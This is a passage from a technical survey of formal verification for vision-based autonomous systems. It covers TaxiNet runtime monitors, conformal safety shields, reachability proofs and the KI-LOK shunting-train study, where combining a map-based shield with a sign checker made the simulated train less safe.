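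3. They merge all the situations that the same sequence of reports could have produced. If any of them is an error, the sequence counts as unsafe.
4. They allow all reports in situations that can never arise, and then delete the error state together with every transition into it.

The second step is the most important. Suppose the airplane is in the right strip, heading right, and the network reports "center, straight". The controller then orders the airplane to go straight, and it leaves the taxiway. The command and the movement follow automatically from the report, so the analysis traces the error back to the report. The assumption must forbid that report in that state, but it cannot forbid the airplane from being there, because perception only observes the airplane's position and does not control it.

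The same analysis yields specifications for single pictures. For an airplane in the right strip and heading right, with actual values marked by a star, the specification is:

(position* = right and heading* = right) ⟹ the report is one of
(center, right), (right, straight), (right, right)

Only the last report is correct, but all three make the controller turn left, which is the only safe command. Under the report probabilities that Păsăreanu and colleagues published for this model, the network reports this state correctly only 31 percent of the time but satisfies the specification 74 percent of the time. The other six reports, which all lead to an error, make up the remaining 26 percent. Boeing's engineers use such specifications to work out requirements for the network, and developers can check them on one labelled picture at a time. Păsăreanu and colleagues also suggest training networks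 to meet this looser target, but have not tried it.

A finer division of the taxiway makes the model much larger, but the assumption grows slowly:

| Strips | Possible reports | States in the model | States in the assumption | Time (seconds) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3 | 9 | 99 | 7 | 0.08 |
| 15 | 45 | 2,151 | 43 | 0.14 |
| 51 | 153 | 23,859 | 151 | 2.9 |
| 101 | 303 | 92,709 | 301 | 81.5 |

The sizes in this table count the combinations of position and heading that the airplane can reach. With three strips and three headings there are nine combinations, but the airplane can never be in the left strip while heading right, or in the right strip while heading left, because it has to be heading outward to get there and can only straighten once it arrives. That leaves seven. With n strips, the same count gives 3n − 2, which matches every row.

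### A monitor that eventually stops the airplane

The states of the assumption thus correspond to the places where the airplane can be, even though Păsăreanu and colleagues designed this version to monitor the network's reports without access to the airplane's actual position. The monitor uses dead reckoning, starting from a known state and using each report to determine the command and each command to determine the next state. It stops the airplane when a report would produce a command that breaks a limit.

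The monitor's guarantee therefore doesn't depend on how accurately the network reads the camera images, but it depends completely on the motion model. If a gust of wind or a slippery patch moves the airplane in a way the model doesn't include, the monitor will track the wrong state and the guarantee will no longer hold.

PRISM confirmed that the model with the monitor never breaks either limit. Păsăreanu and colleagues then used report probabilities from the 11,108 pictures to calculate how often the monitor would intervene. We can work out by hand how likely it is to stop the airplane at the second report. From a centered start, the first report leads to a needless right turn with probability 0.294. After that turn, the next report violates the specification above with probability 0.257. Multiplying these and adding a small contribution from left turns gives a probability of about 7.7 percent.

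Over long runs, the probability that it has stopped the airplane approaches 1. From each of the seven states, at most two unlucky reports are enough to cause a violation. Let p be the smallest probability, over all seven states, of a violation within the next two reports. The probability of no violation in 2n reports is then at most (1 − p)ⁿ, which goes to zero as n grows. A more accurate network makes p smaller and delays the stop. Păsăreanu and colleagues compared two networks and found that the probability of a stop grew much more slowly for the more accurate one, but it approaches 1 for both.

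In this model, the monitor stops the airplane only when the next command would break a limit, so without the monitor the airplane would break a limit exactly as often as the monitor stops it. The monitor turns a safety failure into a liveness failure, meaning the airplane never leaves the taxiway but almost certainly won't finish a long enough route. Pasareanu acknowledges this on the slides, describing the monitor as safe but able to prevent the system from operating. This may be an acceptable trade on a taxiway, where an airplane can brake and wait for a pilot.

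### If the pictures are not representative

Both methods estimate their probabilities from the same 11,108 pictures. Păsăreanu and colleagues explicitly assume that the pictures for each state are independent draws from the distribution the camera will encounter in operation, and that this distribution does not change. But it will change, because light, weather and skid marks differ from one airport to the next and from one hour to the next. The estimate of how often the monitor stops the airplane is then no longer valid, although the monitor's safety proof still holds.

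Pasareanu replies on the slides that the analysis concerns the average case, and that a system should be safe at least there. This is a fair defense of a negative result, because an airplane that often leaves the taxiway under the conditions in the data set can be judged unsafe without analyzing how it behaves in fog. But it gives little support to a positive result, and even the negative result depends on which data were averaged.

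Averaging over all the pictures hides a large difference between bright and dark ones. Watson and colleagues separated Boeing's pictures into these two groups and found that the network estimated the heading correctly in 91 percent of the bright pictures but only 54 percent of the dark ones. For a centered airplane heading straight in the dark, the network output "center, left" 621 times and the correct state only 499 times. This error causes the needless right turn and is the most damaging one in the hand calculation.

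They built a separate Markov chain for each condition and summarized 20 steps of it in a matrix A, which gives the probabilities of ending up in each safe state, and a list b, which gives the probability of failure from each starting state. For a bright stretch followed by a dark one, the failure probabilities are b(bright) + A(bright) · b(dark). The table shows the worst case over 40 steps if the airplane starts centered and straight with a probability of at least 90 percent:

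| First 20 steps | Next 20 steps | Probability of breaking a limit |
|---|---|---|
| bright | bright | 3.0% |
| bright | dark | 32.3% |
| dark | bright | 36.8% |
| dark | dark | 55.1% |
| pooled | pooled | 30.7% |

The pooled row uses a single matrix for all pictures, as the original analysis did. It is ten times too pessimistic for a bright day and much too optimistic for a dark one. It also unrealistically models each picture as bright or dark at random, regardless of the light a moment before.

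Watson and colleagues also prove a bound for conditions that change in an unknown order. Suppose every 20-step stretch, bright or dark, fails with probability at most ε, and an airplane that survives it ends in a condition where the same limit holds for the next stretch. Then the probability of a failure within k stretches is at most 1 − (1 − ε)ᵏ. They could show this for an unpredictable mix of bright and dark with ε = 0.306. The bound is valid but not reassuring, since it reaches 84 percent after five stretches. The approach also requires someone to list the conditions in advance and collect pictures of each, so it doesn't cover snow, for example, if no one collected pictures of it.

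### Intervals that can fail a new environment

*Towards Unified Probabilistic Verification and Validation of Vision-Based Autonomy*, a verification conference paper from October 2025, instead measures whether an old model still fits a new environment. It replaces each probability in the chain with an interval, which makes the chain an interval Markov decision process. In TaxiNet's heading matrix, for example, the network reported "left" for 211 of 1,972 right-heading pictures, which gives a single estimate of 0.107 and a 95 percent interval from about 0.09 to 0.12. The model checker uses the worst value in every interval to compute a lower bound, 1 − β, on the probability that a run is safe.

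When the system moves to a new environment, engineers collect new data there and calculate which report probabilities the data make plausible. The share of these that falls inside the old intervals is the validity confidence, 1 − γ. The guarantee is then that, with confidence 1 − γ, the system is safe with probability at least 1 − β. Wider intervals are more likely to fit a new environment, but they also include worse cases, so the model checker computes a weaker bound on safety.

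The method has not been tried on taxiing. It was tested in simulation on a robot that had to reach a waypoint using noisy estimates of its position. The validity confidence was between 0.65 and 0.78 in four runs in the original environment, and 0 in all ten shifted environments, where the robot's success rate had dropped to between 3 and 50 percent. This separates the two cases cleanly, but the shifts were large, and smaller ones were excluded because it was unclear whether they were really outside the model. The reported confidence is also the median over all states, whereas the theorem covers a more conservative calculation. A median can stay high while a few states go badly wrong, and in TaxiNet the dangerous states are few. The new data must also include the robot's true state, so the method can be used for testing before deployment but not for warnings during it.

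*Assumption Generation* and the closed-loop analysis both use a probability of zero for reports that never occurred, but an interval for such a report runs from zero to slightly above zero. *Automata-Theoretic Verification of Interval Markov Decision Processes* (2026) extends the verification of interval models to all properties in linear temporal logic and finds that intervals starting at zero make the problem harder. With such intervals, the adversary that picks the probabilities can decide whether a transition exists at all, and verification becomes a kind of game.

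### How finely to divide the taxiway

The same robot experiment shows how strongly a guarantee can depend on the size of the grid cells. With cells 1 unit wide, the model checker could guarantee only a 0.036 probability of success. Shrinking the cells to 0.75 units raised the figure to 0.695, and shrinking them to 0.5 units raised it to 0.9998, with no change to the robot. A large cell contains many positions, and the model has to allow for everything that could happen from any of them, including combinations that never occur in practice. A low bound may therefore mean that the system is unsafe or just that the cells are too large.

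Finer cells leave fewer pictures for each state and make the models larger. The 11,108 TaxiNet pictures average about 740 for each of the 15 states, but with 101 strips and three headings there would be about 37 per state, and the estimated probabilities would be much less certain. In the robot experiment, the validity confidence was lower for every finer grid than for the coarsest one, though it did not fall steadily. *Towards Unified Probabilistic Verification and Validation of Vision-Based Autonomy* names the size of the resulting models as the method's main limitation.

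The TaxiNet models avoid the explosion of possibilities in coarse cells by treating all positions within a strip alike and giving each command exactly one result. Watson and colleagues acknowledge that their analysis assumes the report probabilities depend only on the strip, the heading range and the lighting. But an airplane 1.5 meters from the center line is in the center strip and one 1.7 meters away is not, although the two pictures would be nearly identical. Errors probably cluster at such boundaries, and a single probability per strip cannot represent that.

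### Assuming the worst error

*Robust Verification of Controllers under State Uncertainty via Hamilton-Jacobi Reachability Analysis* introduces a framework called RoVer-CoRe, which uses neither strips nor probabilities. It assumes that, at every moment, the position and heading estimates may contain any error within fixed bounds. The framework computes all the states from which some sequence of such errors drives the airplane off the runway. From every other state, the airplane stays on the runway under any sequence of errors within the bounds, whether or not the errors are independent.

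Its taxiing example uses a different network and controller. The airplane moves at 5 meters per second and must stay within 10 meters of the center line for the 20 seconds analyzed. Position and heading can take any value, although the computation uses a fine numerical grid. The steering command is a simple function of the two estimates, so the worst error at each moment can be calculated exactly. When the airplane started on the center line, the framework proved it safe with error bounds wide enough to cover 99.68 percent of the errors in a test set of simulated runway pictures. With bounds covering 99.7 percent, the proof failed for that controller but succeeded for other settings of its two gains. A controller that reacted too strongly to the position estimate overcorrected and steered the airplane off the runway, and one that reacted too strongly to heading could let the airplane drift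 sideways while the estimates showed it aligned.

The guarantee requires every error in the 20 seconds to stay within the bounds, so 99.68 percent coverage does not mean a 99.68 percent chance of a safe run. If the airplane took one picture per second and the errors were independent, about 6 percent of runs would include at least one error outside the bounds. Most of those runs might still be safe, since a single bad estimate rarely lasts long enough to matter, but the proof doesn't cover them. The bounds also come from simulated pictures, so the guarantee still depends on a weaker form of the representativeness premise, which allows new errors to follow a different distribution as long as they are no larger.

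Other methods put a model of the camera back into the proof. Mitra, Păsăreanu and colleagues (2025) survey several of these in *Formal Verification Techniques for Vision-Based Autonomous Systems*. Some describe the camera and the scene geometrically, which ties the proof to one scene. Others train a second network to generate runway pictures from positions and verify the two networks together, so the guarantee covers only pictures the generator can produce. The survey concludes that guarantees based on abstractions built from recorded data, such as confusion matrices, hold only while the system stays within a narrow range of operating conditions. Researchers have also used a taxiing model to test shields that track a set of possible states instead of trusting a single report.

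## Shields and proofs that allow for several possible states

A shield removes the unsafe actions and lets the controller choose among the rest, whereas the monitor in the taxiing study can only stop the airplane. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) adapted shields to controllers that learn by trial and error. Such a controller has to try actions to find out what they do, and without a shield it will try dangerous ones too.

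A shield placed before the learner gives it a list of safe actions at every step, while a shield placed after the learner replaces its chosen action only if that action is unsafe. In both positions, the guarantee covers training as well as later use, and it doesn't depend on how the learner works or how much it has learned.

### Computing which actions are safe

Alshiekh and colleagues treat control as a game. In each round the environment picks an event and the system responds with an action, and the system loses if it ever enters an unsafe state. We can find the losing states by working backwards from the unsafe states, which are all losing. A state is also losing if some event leaves the system with no action that avoids the losing states. Once this process adds no more states, the system has at least one action that avoids the losing states for every event in each remaining state, and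 the shield allows exactly those actions.

Working backwards is necessary because a failure often becomes unavoidable well before it happens. In one example, a car heading toward a cliff has to slow down long before the edge, so a rule that only forbids driving over the edge would take effect too late.

The game needs a model of the surroundings. This model can be coarse and omit anything that doesn't affect safety, but it must include every event that can occur. The guarantee also requires a correct report of the state.

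Suppose a vehicle on a narrow path is near one of the edges. For each action, the table gives the probability that the vehicle soon leaves the path, even if it acts as safely as possible afterwards:

| The vehicle is near | Steer left | Go straight | Steer right |
|---|---|---|---|
| the left edge | 0.60 | 0.08 | 0.01 |
| the right edge | 0.01 | 0.08 | 0.60 |

A shield that allows probabilities up to 0.1 lets a vehicle near the left edge go straight or steer right. If perception reports the left edge while the vehicle is near the right one, the shield blocks steering left, which is the safest action, and allows steering right, which takes the vehicle off the path 60 percent of the time. A shield that receives a wrong report can therefore be worse than no shield, because it can block the safest action when the controller would have chosen it.

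### Allowing only what is safe in every possible state

In *Conformal Safety Shielding for Imperfect-Perception Agents* (Scarbro, Imrie and colleagues, 2025), perception returns a set of states instead of a single one. The shield allows an action only if it is safe in every state in the set.

The sets come from conformal prediction, a method that outputs a set of answers containing the true one with a chosen probability 1 − α, if new data resemble the calibration data. For a network that assigns a probability to each state, the standard procedure is as follows:

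1. Collect N pictures that the network has not seen in training, each labelled with its true state.
2. Score each picture as 1 minus the probability that the network gave to the true state, so that a high score means a bad mistake.
3. Sort the scores from low to high and take the one at position (N + 1)(1 − α), rounded up, as the cutoff.
4. For a new picture, return every state that would score at or below the cutoff.

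If the new picture comes from the same source as the others, its score is equally likely to land at any of the N + 1 possible positions in the sorted list. The score is therefore at or below the cutoff with probability at least 1 − α, and whenever it is, the set contains the true state. This argument requires no model of the camera or the network. The guarantee holds even if the network is poor, but the sets are larger.

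The shield itself starts from a score σ(s, a) for taking action a in state s. This is the probability of reaching an unsafe state within a fixed number of further steps, called the lookahead, if the system behaves as safely as possible after a. With a threshold λ, the allowed actions are:

for one state: Δ(s) = {a : σ(s, a) ≤ λ}
for a set of states: the actions that belong to Δ(s) for every s in the set

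In the narrow-path example, suppose λ is 0.1 and perception returns both edges. Steering either way is too dangerous in one of the two states, so the shield allows only going straight. This is sensible when nobody can tell which edge is near.

If λ is lowered to 0.05, going straight is no longer acceptable because it scores 0.08, so the shield allows no action. Each state on its own still has an acceptable action, with a score of 0.01, but the two states need opposite actions. Scarbro and colleagues call a state with no allowed action a stuck state. They leave open what the machine should do there, but mention taking another reading, halting or alerting a human operator.

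The robot at the door always has an allowed action, since staying put is safe whether the door is open or closed. For an aircraft in flight, having no allowed action is itself a safety problem.

Other shields combine all the observations so far into an estimate of where the machine might be. This can rule out states that a single picture cannot, but as Scarbro and colleagues point out, it requires a model of how each state produces observations, or at least of which observations each state can produce. Such a model is usually infeasible for camera images. Their shield avoids the need for one by using only the latest picture.

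### A bound that weakens with every step

The main theorem in the paper, Theorem 1, concerns perfect perception. It assumes that the starting state has at least one allowed action and that the system never reaches a stuck state. Then, for any controller that stays within the shield, the probability of reaching an unsafe state within n steps is at most:

1 − (1 − λ)ⁿ

With λ = 0.1, the bound is 10 percent for one step, 41 percent for five and 65 percent for ten. For 30 steps it is 1 − 0.9³⁰, or about 95.8 percent, which guarantees very little. To keep the bound below 5 percent over 30 steps, λ would have to be about 0.0017, and a shield that strict would often block every action.

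The bound decays because σ scores each action as if the safest possible behavior followed it, while the shield doesn't require the controller to behave that way. Scarbro and colleagues show with a two-state example that no better bound holds in general. In the safe state, one action carries no risk, while another fails with probability λ and otherwise returns to the same state. The risky action scores exactly λ, so the shield allows it every time, and a controller that keeps choosing it fails with exactly the probability in the theorem. A longer lookahead doesn't help, because the risky action still scores λ. A controller that prefers the safest allowed action may do far better than the bound, but the theorem covers every controller that the shield permits.

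Earlier probabilistic shields compared each action with the safest one available in the same state. They always allowed at least one action, but gave no overall guarantee, since even the safest action in a state may be almost certain to fail. Scarbro and colleagues apply the same threshold in every state, which lets them prove an overall guarantee but can leave some states with no allowed action.

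The assumption that the system never gets stuck is a strong one, even with perfect perception. Suppose the lookahead is five steps and a car is on a one-way road that ends at a cliff, with no way to stop or turn. Seven steps from the cliff, driving on scores 0, because the car will still be on the road five steps after that move. One step later, driving on scores 1 and the shield blocks it, so the car was certain to get stuck. The game of Alshiekh and colleagues avoids this because it has no horizon and classifies the whole road as losing from the start. Scarbro and colleagues show that the probability of getting stuck has no general upper bound below 1. They recommend calculating it for each system before deployment and adjusting λ or the lookahead if it is too high.

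### Why the proof stops at perfect perception

For imperfect perception, Scarbro and colleagues first want to prove a more modest, single-step claim that an allowed action has a score of at most λ in the actual state with probability at least 1 − α. This seems to follow directly, since the set contains the actual state with that probability and the shield checks every state in the set.

However, 1 − α is an average over pictures like those in the calibration data, which come from a system that has no shield and picks its actions at random. Adding the shield changes the actions, which changes the states the system visits and the pictures it takes.

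For instance, suppose 90 percent of the calibration pictures show the center of a taxiway and 10 percent show the edge. If the sets contain the true state for 99 percent of the center pictures and 59 percent of the edge pictures, the overall figure is the promised 95 percent. If the shielded system spends half its time near the edge, the figure drops to 79 percent. A good shield should keep the system away from the edge, which would raise the figure, but the claim has to hold for every controller that stays within the shield, including one that drifts outward whenever the shield allows it.

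Scarbro and colleagues propose to repeat the calibration by running the shielded system in simulation, collecting new pictures, recalibrating, and running it again. But each recalibration changes the sets, which changes the shield and therefore the states visited. They leave for future work whether this procedure can support a proof. They also leave open a bound for whole runs like the one in Theorem 1.

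Such a bound would also have to account for sets that miss the true state, since the chance of at least one miss grows with the length of the run. If the misses are independent, the probability that all 30 sets in a 30-step run contain the true state is 21 percent when each set has 95 percent confidence, and 86 percent when each has 99.5 percent confidence.

### Fewer failures and more stuck runs

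To test the shield, Scarbro and colleagues used the 15-state taxiing model, with a small simulated robot in place of the airplane. They collected 5,500 pictures with the robot at random positions on a simulated taxiway and set aside 15 percent for calibration and another 15 percent for testing. In the model, the airplane follows each command with probability 0.9 and makes each of the other two moves with probability 0.05.

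They tried confidence levels of 95, 99 and 99.5 percent and values of λ from 0.1 to 0.3, with a lookahead of five steps. For runs of up to 30 steps, they used PRISM to compute the probabilities that the airplane fails, gets stuck or completes the run. They compared the results with those of a shield that treats the network's single best estimate as the true state. That shield always allowed at least one action, so the airplane never got stuck.

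The set-based shield generally failed less often than the comparison shield. Higher confidence reduced failures, but it also made the sets larger and left the airplane stuck more often. Lowering λ had a similar effect. At 95 percent confidence, the airplane seldom got stuck and completed more runs than with the comparison shield. At the two higher confidence levels, it was very likely to get stuck and completed fewer.

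The shield's low failure rates at high confidence overstate its benefit, because a run that gets stuck ends there and can no longer fail. The result at 95 percent is better evidence for the method, because the shield also increased the number of completed runs at that level. The cutoffs for high confidence also depend on very few pictures. With 825 calibration pictures, the standard procedure sets the 99.5 percent cutoff at the 822nd-lowest score, so only the three worst pictures lie above it.

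The experiment doesn't test the problem that blocks the proof. PRISM used a confusion matrix that gives the probability of each set in each state. The counts for the matrix came from the test pictures, which show the same random positions as the calibration pictures. Within a state, the model therefore uses the same probabilities of perception errors whatever route the airplane took to get there.

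The method also scales poorly with the number of states. Fifteen states can form 32,767 non-empty sets, and each additional state roughly doubles that number. Scarbro and colleagues suggest computing the allowed actions only for sets that come up during operation.

### Choosing the size of the set from the safety requirement

A position in meters can take infinitely many values, so perception can return a range of possible states but not a list of them. *Verifying Controllers with Convolutional Neural Network-based Perception* (Hsieh, Misailovic and colleagues, 2021) works out how wide that range can be without endangering the system. This is similar to finding the weakest assumption on the taxiing network's reports, but for continuous values.

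They divide the state space into cells and describe acceptable perception in each cell by a ball. If z* is the correct reading, such as the car's true distance and angle from the lane center, the network's reading z is acceptable when:

‖z − (A·z* + b)‖ ≤ r

A and b come from a linear regression on the network's actual outputs, so the center of the ball includes any systematic bias. To set the radius r, an optimizer searches the cell for the reading closest to the center that would make the controller violate the safety requirement, and r is set just below the distance to that reading. Any perception system whose readings always stay inside the balls is then safe. Hsieh and colleagues confirmed this by checking the code of the controller and the vehicle model with CBMC, a verification tool for C programs.

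The proof does not establish whether the real network's readings stay inside the balls, so the researchers measured how often they do. In a simulated electric car that used a network to find lane markings, readings fell inside the ball more than 90 percent of the time in several cells of the finest grid. *Verifying Controllers with Vision-based Perception Using Safe Approximate Abstractions*, a second version of the work by Hsieh, Li and colleagues, adds a statistical lower bound on the true rate. Neither figure is the probability that the car is safe, because the test pictures came from evenly spread positions and chosen road types, and a real car would encounter a different mix.

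In other cells, hardly any readings fell inside, including those where the car was centered in its lane and pointing straight. This happened because the proof by Hsieh and colleagues requires that the car's combined error in distance and angle not increase from one step to the next. When that error is nearly zero, even a tiny mistake in perception increases it, so r shrinks to almost nothing. A car in the middle of its lane is in no danger, so the proof fails there because its requirement is stricter than safety requires. Hsieh and colleagues found the same pattern in a farm robot that drives between rows of corn. When they measured the car's error in other ways, the failing cells moved to where the new measure was close to zero.

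### Error bounds that vary with the state

We can also estimate the size of the set of possible states from data, then check whether the system is safe with perception errors of that size. A single error bound for all states tends to be too loose for this, because it has to cover the states where perception is worst. *State-Dependent Conformal Perception Bounds for Neuro-Symbolic Verification of Autonomous Systems* (Waite, Geng and colleagues, 2025) divides the state space into regions and gives each its own bound.

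The method calibrates on whole runs instead of single pictures. For each run, it records the largest perception error in each region, and conformal prediction turns these maxima into a bound for that region. The probability that a region's bound fails at any time during a new run is at most α/M. Adding these probabilities over the M regions gives a probability of at most α that any bound fails during the run. A reachability tool then computes every state the system can reach if the errors stay within the bounds. With α = 0.05, the actual run stays inside the computed states from start to finish with probability at least 95 percent.

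This avoids both problems that Scarbro and colleagues encountered. The guarantee doesn't decay with each step, because the calibration data consist of complete runs of the intended length. The data also match the states that the system visits, because Waite and colleagues record them with the same controller that they verify. However, the guarantee applies only to that controller. Retraining it or adding a shield requires collecting new runs. Waite and colleagues leave it to future work to calibrate with one controller and deploy another, or to calibrate in simulation and deploy in the real world.

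The test case is Mountain Car, a standard exercise in which a weak car must rock back and forth to get up a hill. A network trained on pictures without blur estimates the car's position from blurred ones. An algorithm chose the boundaries of the regions to keep the computed sets of states small. With seven regions, the largest set over 90 steps was 0.115 wide, compared with 0.225 for an existing method whose bounds vary with time instead of state. The computation took about five times as long, partly because whenever the set of possible states straddles a boundary between regions, the tool has to follow each part separately.

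The follow-up, *Statistical-Symbolic Verification of Perception-Based Autonomous Systems using State-Dependent Conformal Prediction*, lets the regions have different confidence levels and gives the competing method more data for tuning. That narrows the gap:

| Test case | Measure | Bounds by state | Bounds by time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mountain Car | widths of the sets, summed over all steps | 4.360 | 5.508 |
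| Mountain Car | largest width | 0.115 | 0.177 |
| Mountain Car | computing time | 256 hours | 48 hours |
| Model racing car | total area of the sets | 2.456 m² | 2.469 m² |
| Model racing car | verified distance from the wall | 20.95 cm | 19.82 cm |
| Model racing car | computing time | 212.5 hours | 195.5 hours |

The table shows the best result of each method by total size. The racing car is a tenth of full size and uses laser distance measurements to get around a corner. Its improvement in area is only half a percent, but the extra centimeter from the wall is more useful, since that is where a collision would happen. Most of the computing time went into a controller that always steers fully left or right, because the tool had to follow both possibilities whenever the sign of the estimated error was uncertain.

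### Acting on the riskiest possible state

The methods of Hsieh and Waite check a system before deployment and leave its behavior unchanged. Miao, Darir and Mitra (2026), in *Correcting Learning-based Perception for Safety*, use a set of possible states while the vehicle is driving. They start from a perception contract M, which lists the readings that perception may produce in each state, much like the balls above. Turning it around gives the states that could lie behind a reading y:

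M⁻¹(y) = {x : y ∈ M(x)}

The car then picks the riskiest state in this set and acts as if it were there. If it might be 20 or 30 meters behind another car, for example, it brakes as if the distance were 20 meters. Unlike the shield of Scarbro and colleagues, this method has an action to take whenever the set contains a state from which the car can still stay safe.

Miao and colleagues prove that the car stays safe if the set of possible states always contains the true one and any action that is safe in a riskier state is also safe in a less risky one. Braking naturally meets the second condition, since braking hard enough to stop within 20 meters also stops the car within 30. The condition is much harder to meet for steering. On the narrow path, steering right is safe at the left edge and dangerous at the right edge, and the reverse is true of steering left, so the condition fails whichever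 edge we call riskier.

They tested the correction in a driving simulator, on a car that had to stay in its lane and keep its distance from the car ahead. Three road shapes, six kinds of weather and three controllers made 54 scenarios. The car completed all of them safely when it received exact positions. When it used neural networks for perception, it was safe only in the 9 scenarios with clear skies, and it collided or left its lane in the other 45. The correction made 33 of these 45 scenarios safe (73 percent), and those 33 runs took 2.8 percent longer on average than with exact positions.

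The logs of the 12 remaining failures show that the true state was outside the predicted set at some point, so the theorem did not apply. Nine of these failures occurred with one controller and three with another, while the third controller was safe in all 15 of its foggy or rainy scenarios.

Miao and colleagues estimate the sets with a second neural network, trained on about 5,000 pairs of readings and true states. On new data, the sets contained the true state 91.2 percent of the time. At that rate, many of the 33 rescued runs probably included some sets that didn't contain the true state, so the correction seems to work in considerably more cases than its proof covers.

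## An autonomous shunting train: verified steering with a real detector

Researchers in the German project KI-LOK (2021–2024) combined two safeguards on a self-driving locomotive in a shunting yard, where railway staff sort and park trains. In simulation, the train was less safe with both safeguards than with one of them alone. The locomotive must stop at an Sh0 signal and may pass an Sh1 signal, which means the track is free. Hitachi Rail supplied the case study, and a group at Heinrich Heine University Düsseldorf built the formal model.

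### Steering that is safe if perception is correct

A neural network finds signals, switches and obstacles in camera images, and a conventional program decides how far the train may move. In their final report on the project, *Prüfverfahren für KI-basierte Komponenten im Eisenbahnbetrieb*, Leuschel, Gruteser and Roßbach (2024) treat the network as a black box and model only its outputs.

They wrote the model in the B method, which describes a system by its variables, the operations that change them, and an invariant, a condition that must always hold. Engineers state all of these in logic and set theory, then prove that the starting state satisfies the invariant and that every operation preserves it. Industry has used B for more than 25 years, often for railways. The group also used ProB, a model checker for B, to check this temporal-logic formula:

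always (the train moves forward → one step earlier, the controller chose to move forward and the train had correctly detected all signals, switches, obstacles and the course of the track)
→ always (no safety-critical situation)

Everything before the last arrow is the premise, and most of it concerns perception. If the train moves forward even once after misreading a signal, even if no harm results, the premise is false for the whole run and the formula guarantees nothing about that run. ProB verified the formula only for reduced versions of the model, such as one in which the train is given the signals' locations. The full model had too many states, so the group used simulation instead.

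Gruteser, Roßbach and colleagues (2024), in *Using Formal Models, Safety Shields and Certified Control*, connected the B model to a real detector. They used YOLOv8, a widely used object-detection network, and trained it further on railway signs. Each step of the simulation works like this:

1. The program picks a random video picture that fits the train's position and the current state of the signals.
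2. YOLO processes the picture. If it detects a signal, the controller receives "stop" or "permission" and recalculates how far the train may go. If it detects none, the controller receives nothing.
3. With probability 75 percent the train moves forward. Otherwise something in the yard changes, for example a signal.

The TaxiNet analysis used a confusion matrix in place of the network. Here the network itself runs in the loop, so nobody has to estimate its error rates beforehand.

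### A map and a sign checker

The detector can report a signal that isn't there or confuse one signal with another, and the group counts both as false positives. It can also miss a signal, which is a false negative. A false "stop" only delays the train, but a false "track free" or a missed stop signal can cause a collision.

The shield uses a map of the yard to catch missed signals. If the detector finds nothing where the map shows a signal, the shield blocks forward movement and the train stops in front of the signal. The shield also ignores detections where the map shows no signal.

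The checker is meant to catch false positives. It follows an architecture called certified control, in which the network must supply evidence for its answer and a much simpler program verifies that evidence. In *Certified control for train sign classification* (Roßbach and Leuschel, 2025), the evidence is the picture, the reported type of sign and a box around the sign. The checker handles three signs, each with two half-circles whose angle differs by sign: 0 degrees for Sh0, 45 for Sh1 and 90 for Wn7, which also permits passage.

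The checker cuts out the box, converts it to gray and traces the outlines in it with standard image-processing routines. It accepts the sign if it finds two separate outlines of similar size and direction that lie within 18 degrees of the expected angle. Sh1 therefore covers angles from 27 to 63 degrees and Sh0 covers angles up to 18 degrees, so the same pair of shapes can't pass as both.

Roßbach and Leuschel tested the checker on 74,935 signs that they had distorted and pasted into pictures from real train rides. They used three sizes of YOLO network:

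| Network | False positives without checker | False positives with checker | Correct detections without checker | Correct detections with checker |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| nano | 17,440 | 1 | 40,563 | 32,902 |
| small | 3,044 | 1 | 49,052 | 39,843 |
| medium | 10,135 | 0 | 41,598 | 37,793 |

The checker removed all but 2 of 30,619 false positives, but it also rejected between 9 and 19 percent of the correct detections, so the system missed signs that the network had found. Roßbach and Leuschel acknowledge this and recommend other measures against missed signs, such as a map.

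They hope to prove that the program implements its rules correctly, but have not yet done so. Such a proof would not show that a sign is there, because anything with two suitable shapes at the right angle passes the check. It also would not show that the sign applies to this train. *Certified Control for Train Sign Classification* (Roßbach and Leuschel, 2023), the first version of the work, does not address which signals are relevant, and a genuine Sh1 beside the neighboring track would also pass.

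### Three thousand simulated runs

Gruteser and colleagues ran 500 simulations for each combination of safeguards. They also tried a checker that doesn't examine stop signals and so can never reject a real one. A run ended when a safety-critical situation occurred or when the train could go no farther. The last two columns are totals over 500 runs:

| Shield | Checker | Safe runs | Distance traveled | False detections | Correct detections |
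|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| no | none | 100% | 6.4 | 500 | – |
| no | all but stop signals | 100% | 6.1 | 500 | – |
| no | all signals | 63.2% | 221.2 | 0 | 2,335 |
| yes | none | 82.8% | 247.8 | 20,611 | 9,155 |
| yes | all but stop signals | 80.4% | 247.0 | 20,993 | 8,929 |
| yes | all signals | 63.0% | 216.8 | 0 | 2,094 |

Without safeguards, every run was safe because the train hardly moved. The detector reported nonexistent stop signals so often that each run ended at the first false report, before the train came near a real signal.

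Either safeguard gets the train moving, since the shield ignores most of these false stops and the checker rejects them. But a moving train can overrun real signals. With the shield alone, 86 of the 500 runs were unsafe, compared with 184 with the checker alone and 185 with both. The difference between 86 and 185 is far too large to be chance.

### How a rejected stop sign leads to an overrun

Gruteser and colleagues had not expected the combination to do worse than the shield alone, so they inspected the runs in ProB. A typical overrun develops as follows:

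1. The train approaches a signal that shows Sh1. The detector reports it, the checker accepts it and the controller allows the train to pass. Because the detector has found a signal at the known position, the shield no longer blocks movement.
2. The signal changes to Sh0.
3. The detector correctly reports "stop", but the checker can't confirm the sign and rejects it.
4. The controller receives nothing, so the earlier permission still stands and the train passes the stop signal.

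The results for the checker that ignores stop signals support this explanation. With the shield on, that change alone raised the share of safe runs from 63.0 to 80.4 percent and the number of correct detections from 2,094 to 8,929. The detection count depends partly on how long the runs last, but such a large increase suggests that the checker rejected many more real stop signs in these videos than in the generated pictures.

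The shield alone doesn't prevent this kind of overrun either, because the detector can miss the change to "stop" even without the checker. Such misses probably account for many of the 86 unsafe runs. According to the final report, the shield reduces the effect of wrong rejections, but the table shows no such benefit, with 63.2 percent of runs safe without the shield and 63.0 percent safe with it.

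The underlying mistake is treating a rejected detection as no detection. Ignoring a rejected "track free" sign is cautious, but ignoring a rejected "stop" sign discards the only evidence against moving. Under Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, only a permission should need a certificate. A permission could also expire unless the detector keeps confirming it. Gruteser and colleagues did not test this, and it would make the train stop more often.

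The percentages don't carry over to a real yard. Something in the simulated yard changed in about a quarter of the steps, and the group wanted a detector that made mistakes so they could study the safeguards. Each step also used a new random picture, so the simulation leaves out causes of error that last for a whole approach, like the glare in the door example.

### Certifying only permission to move

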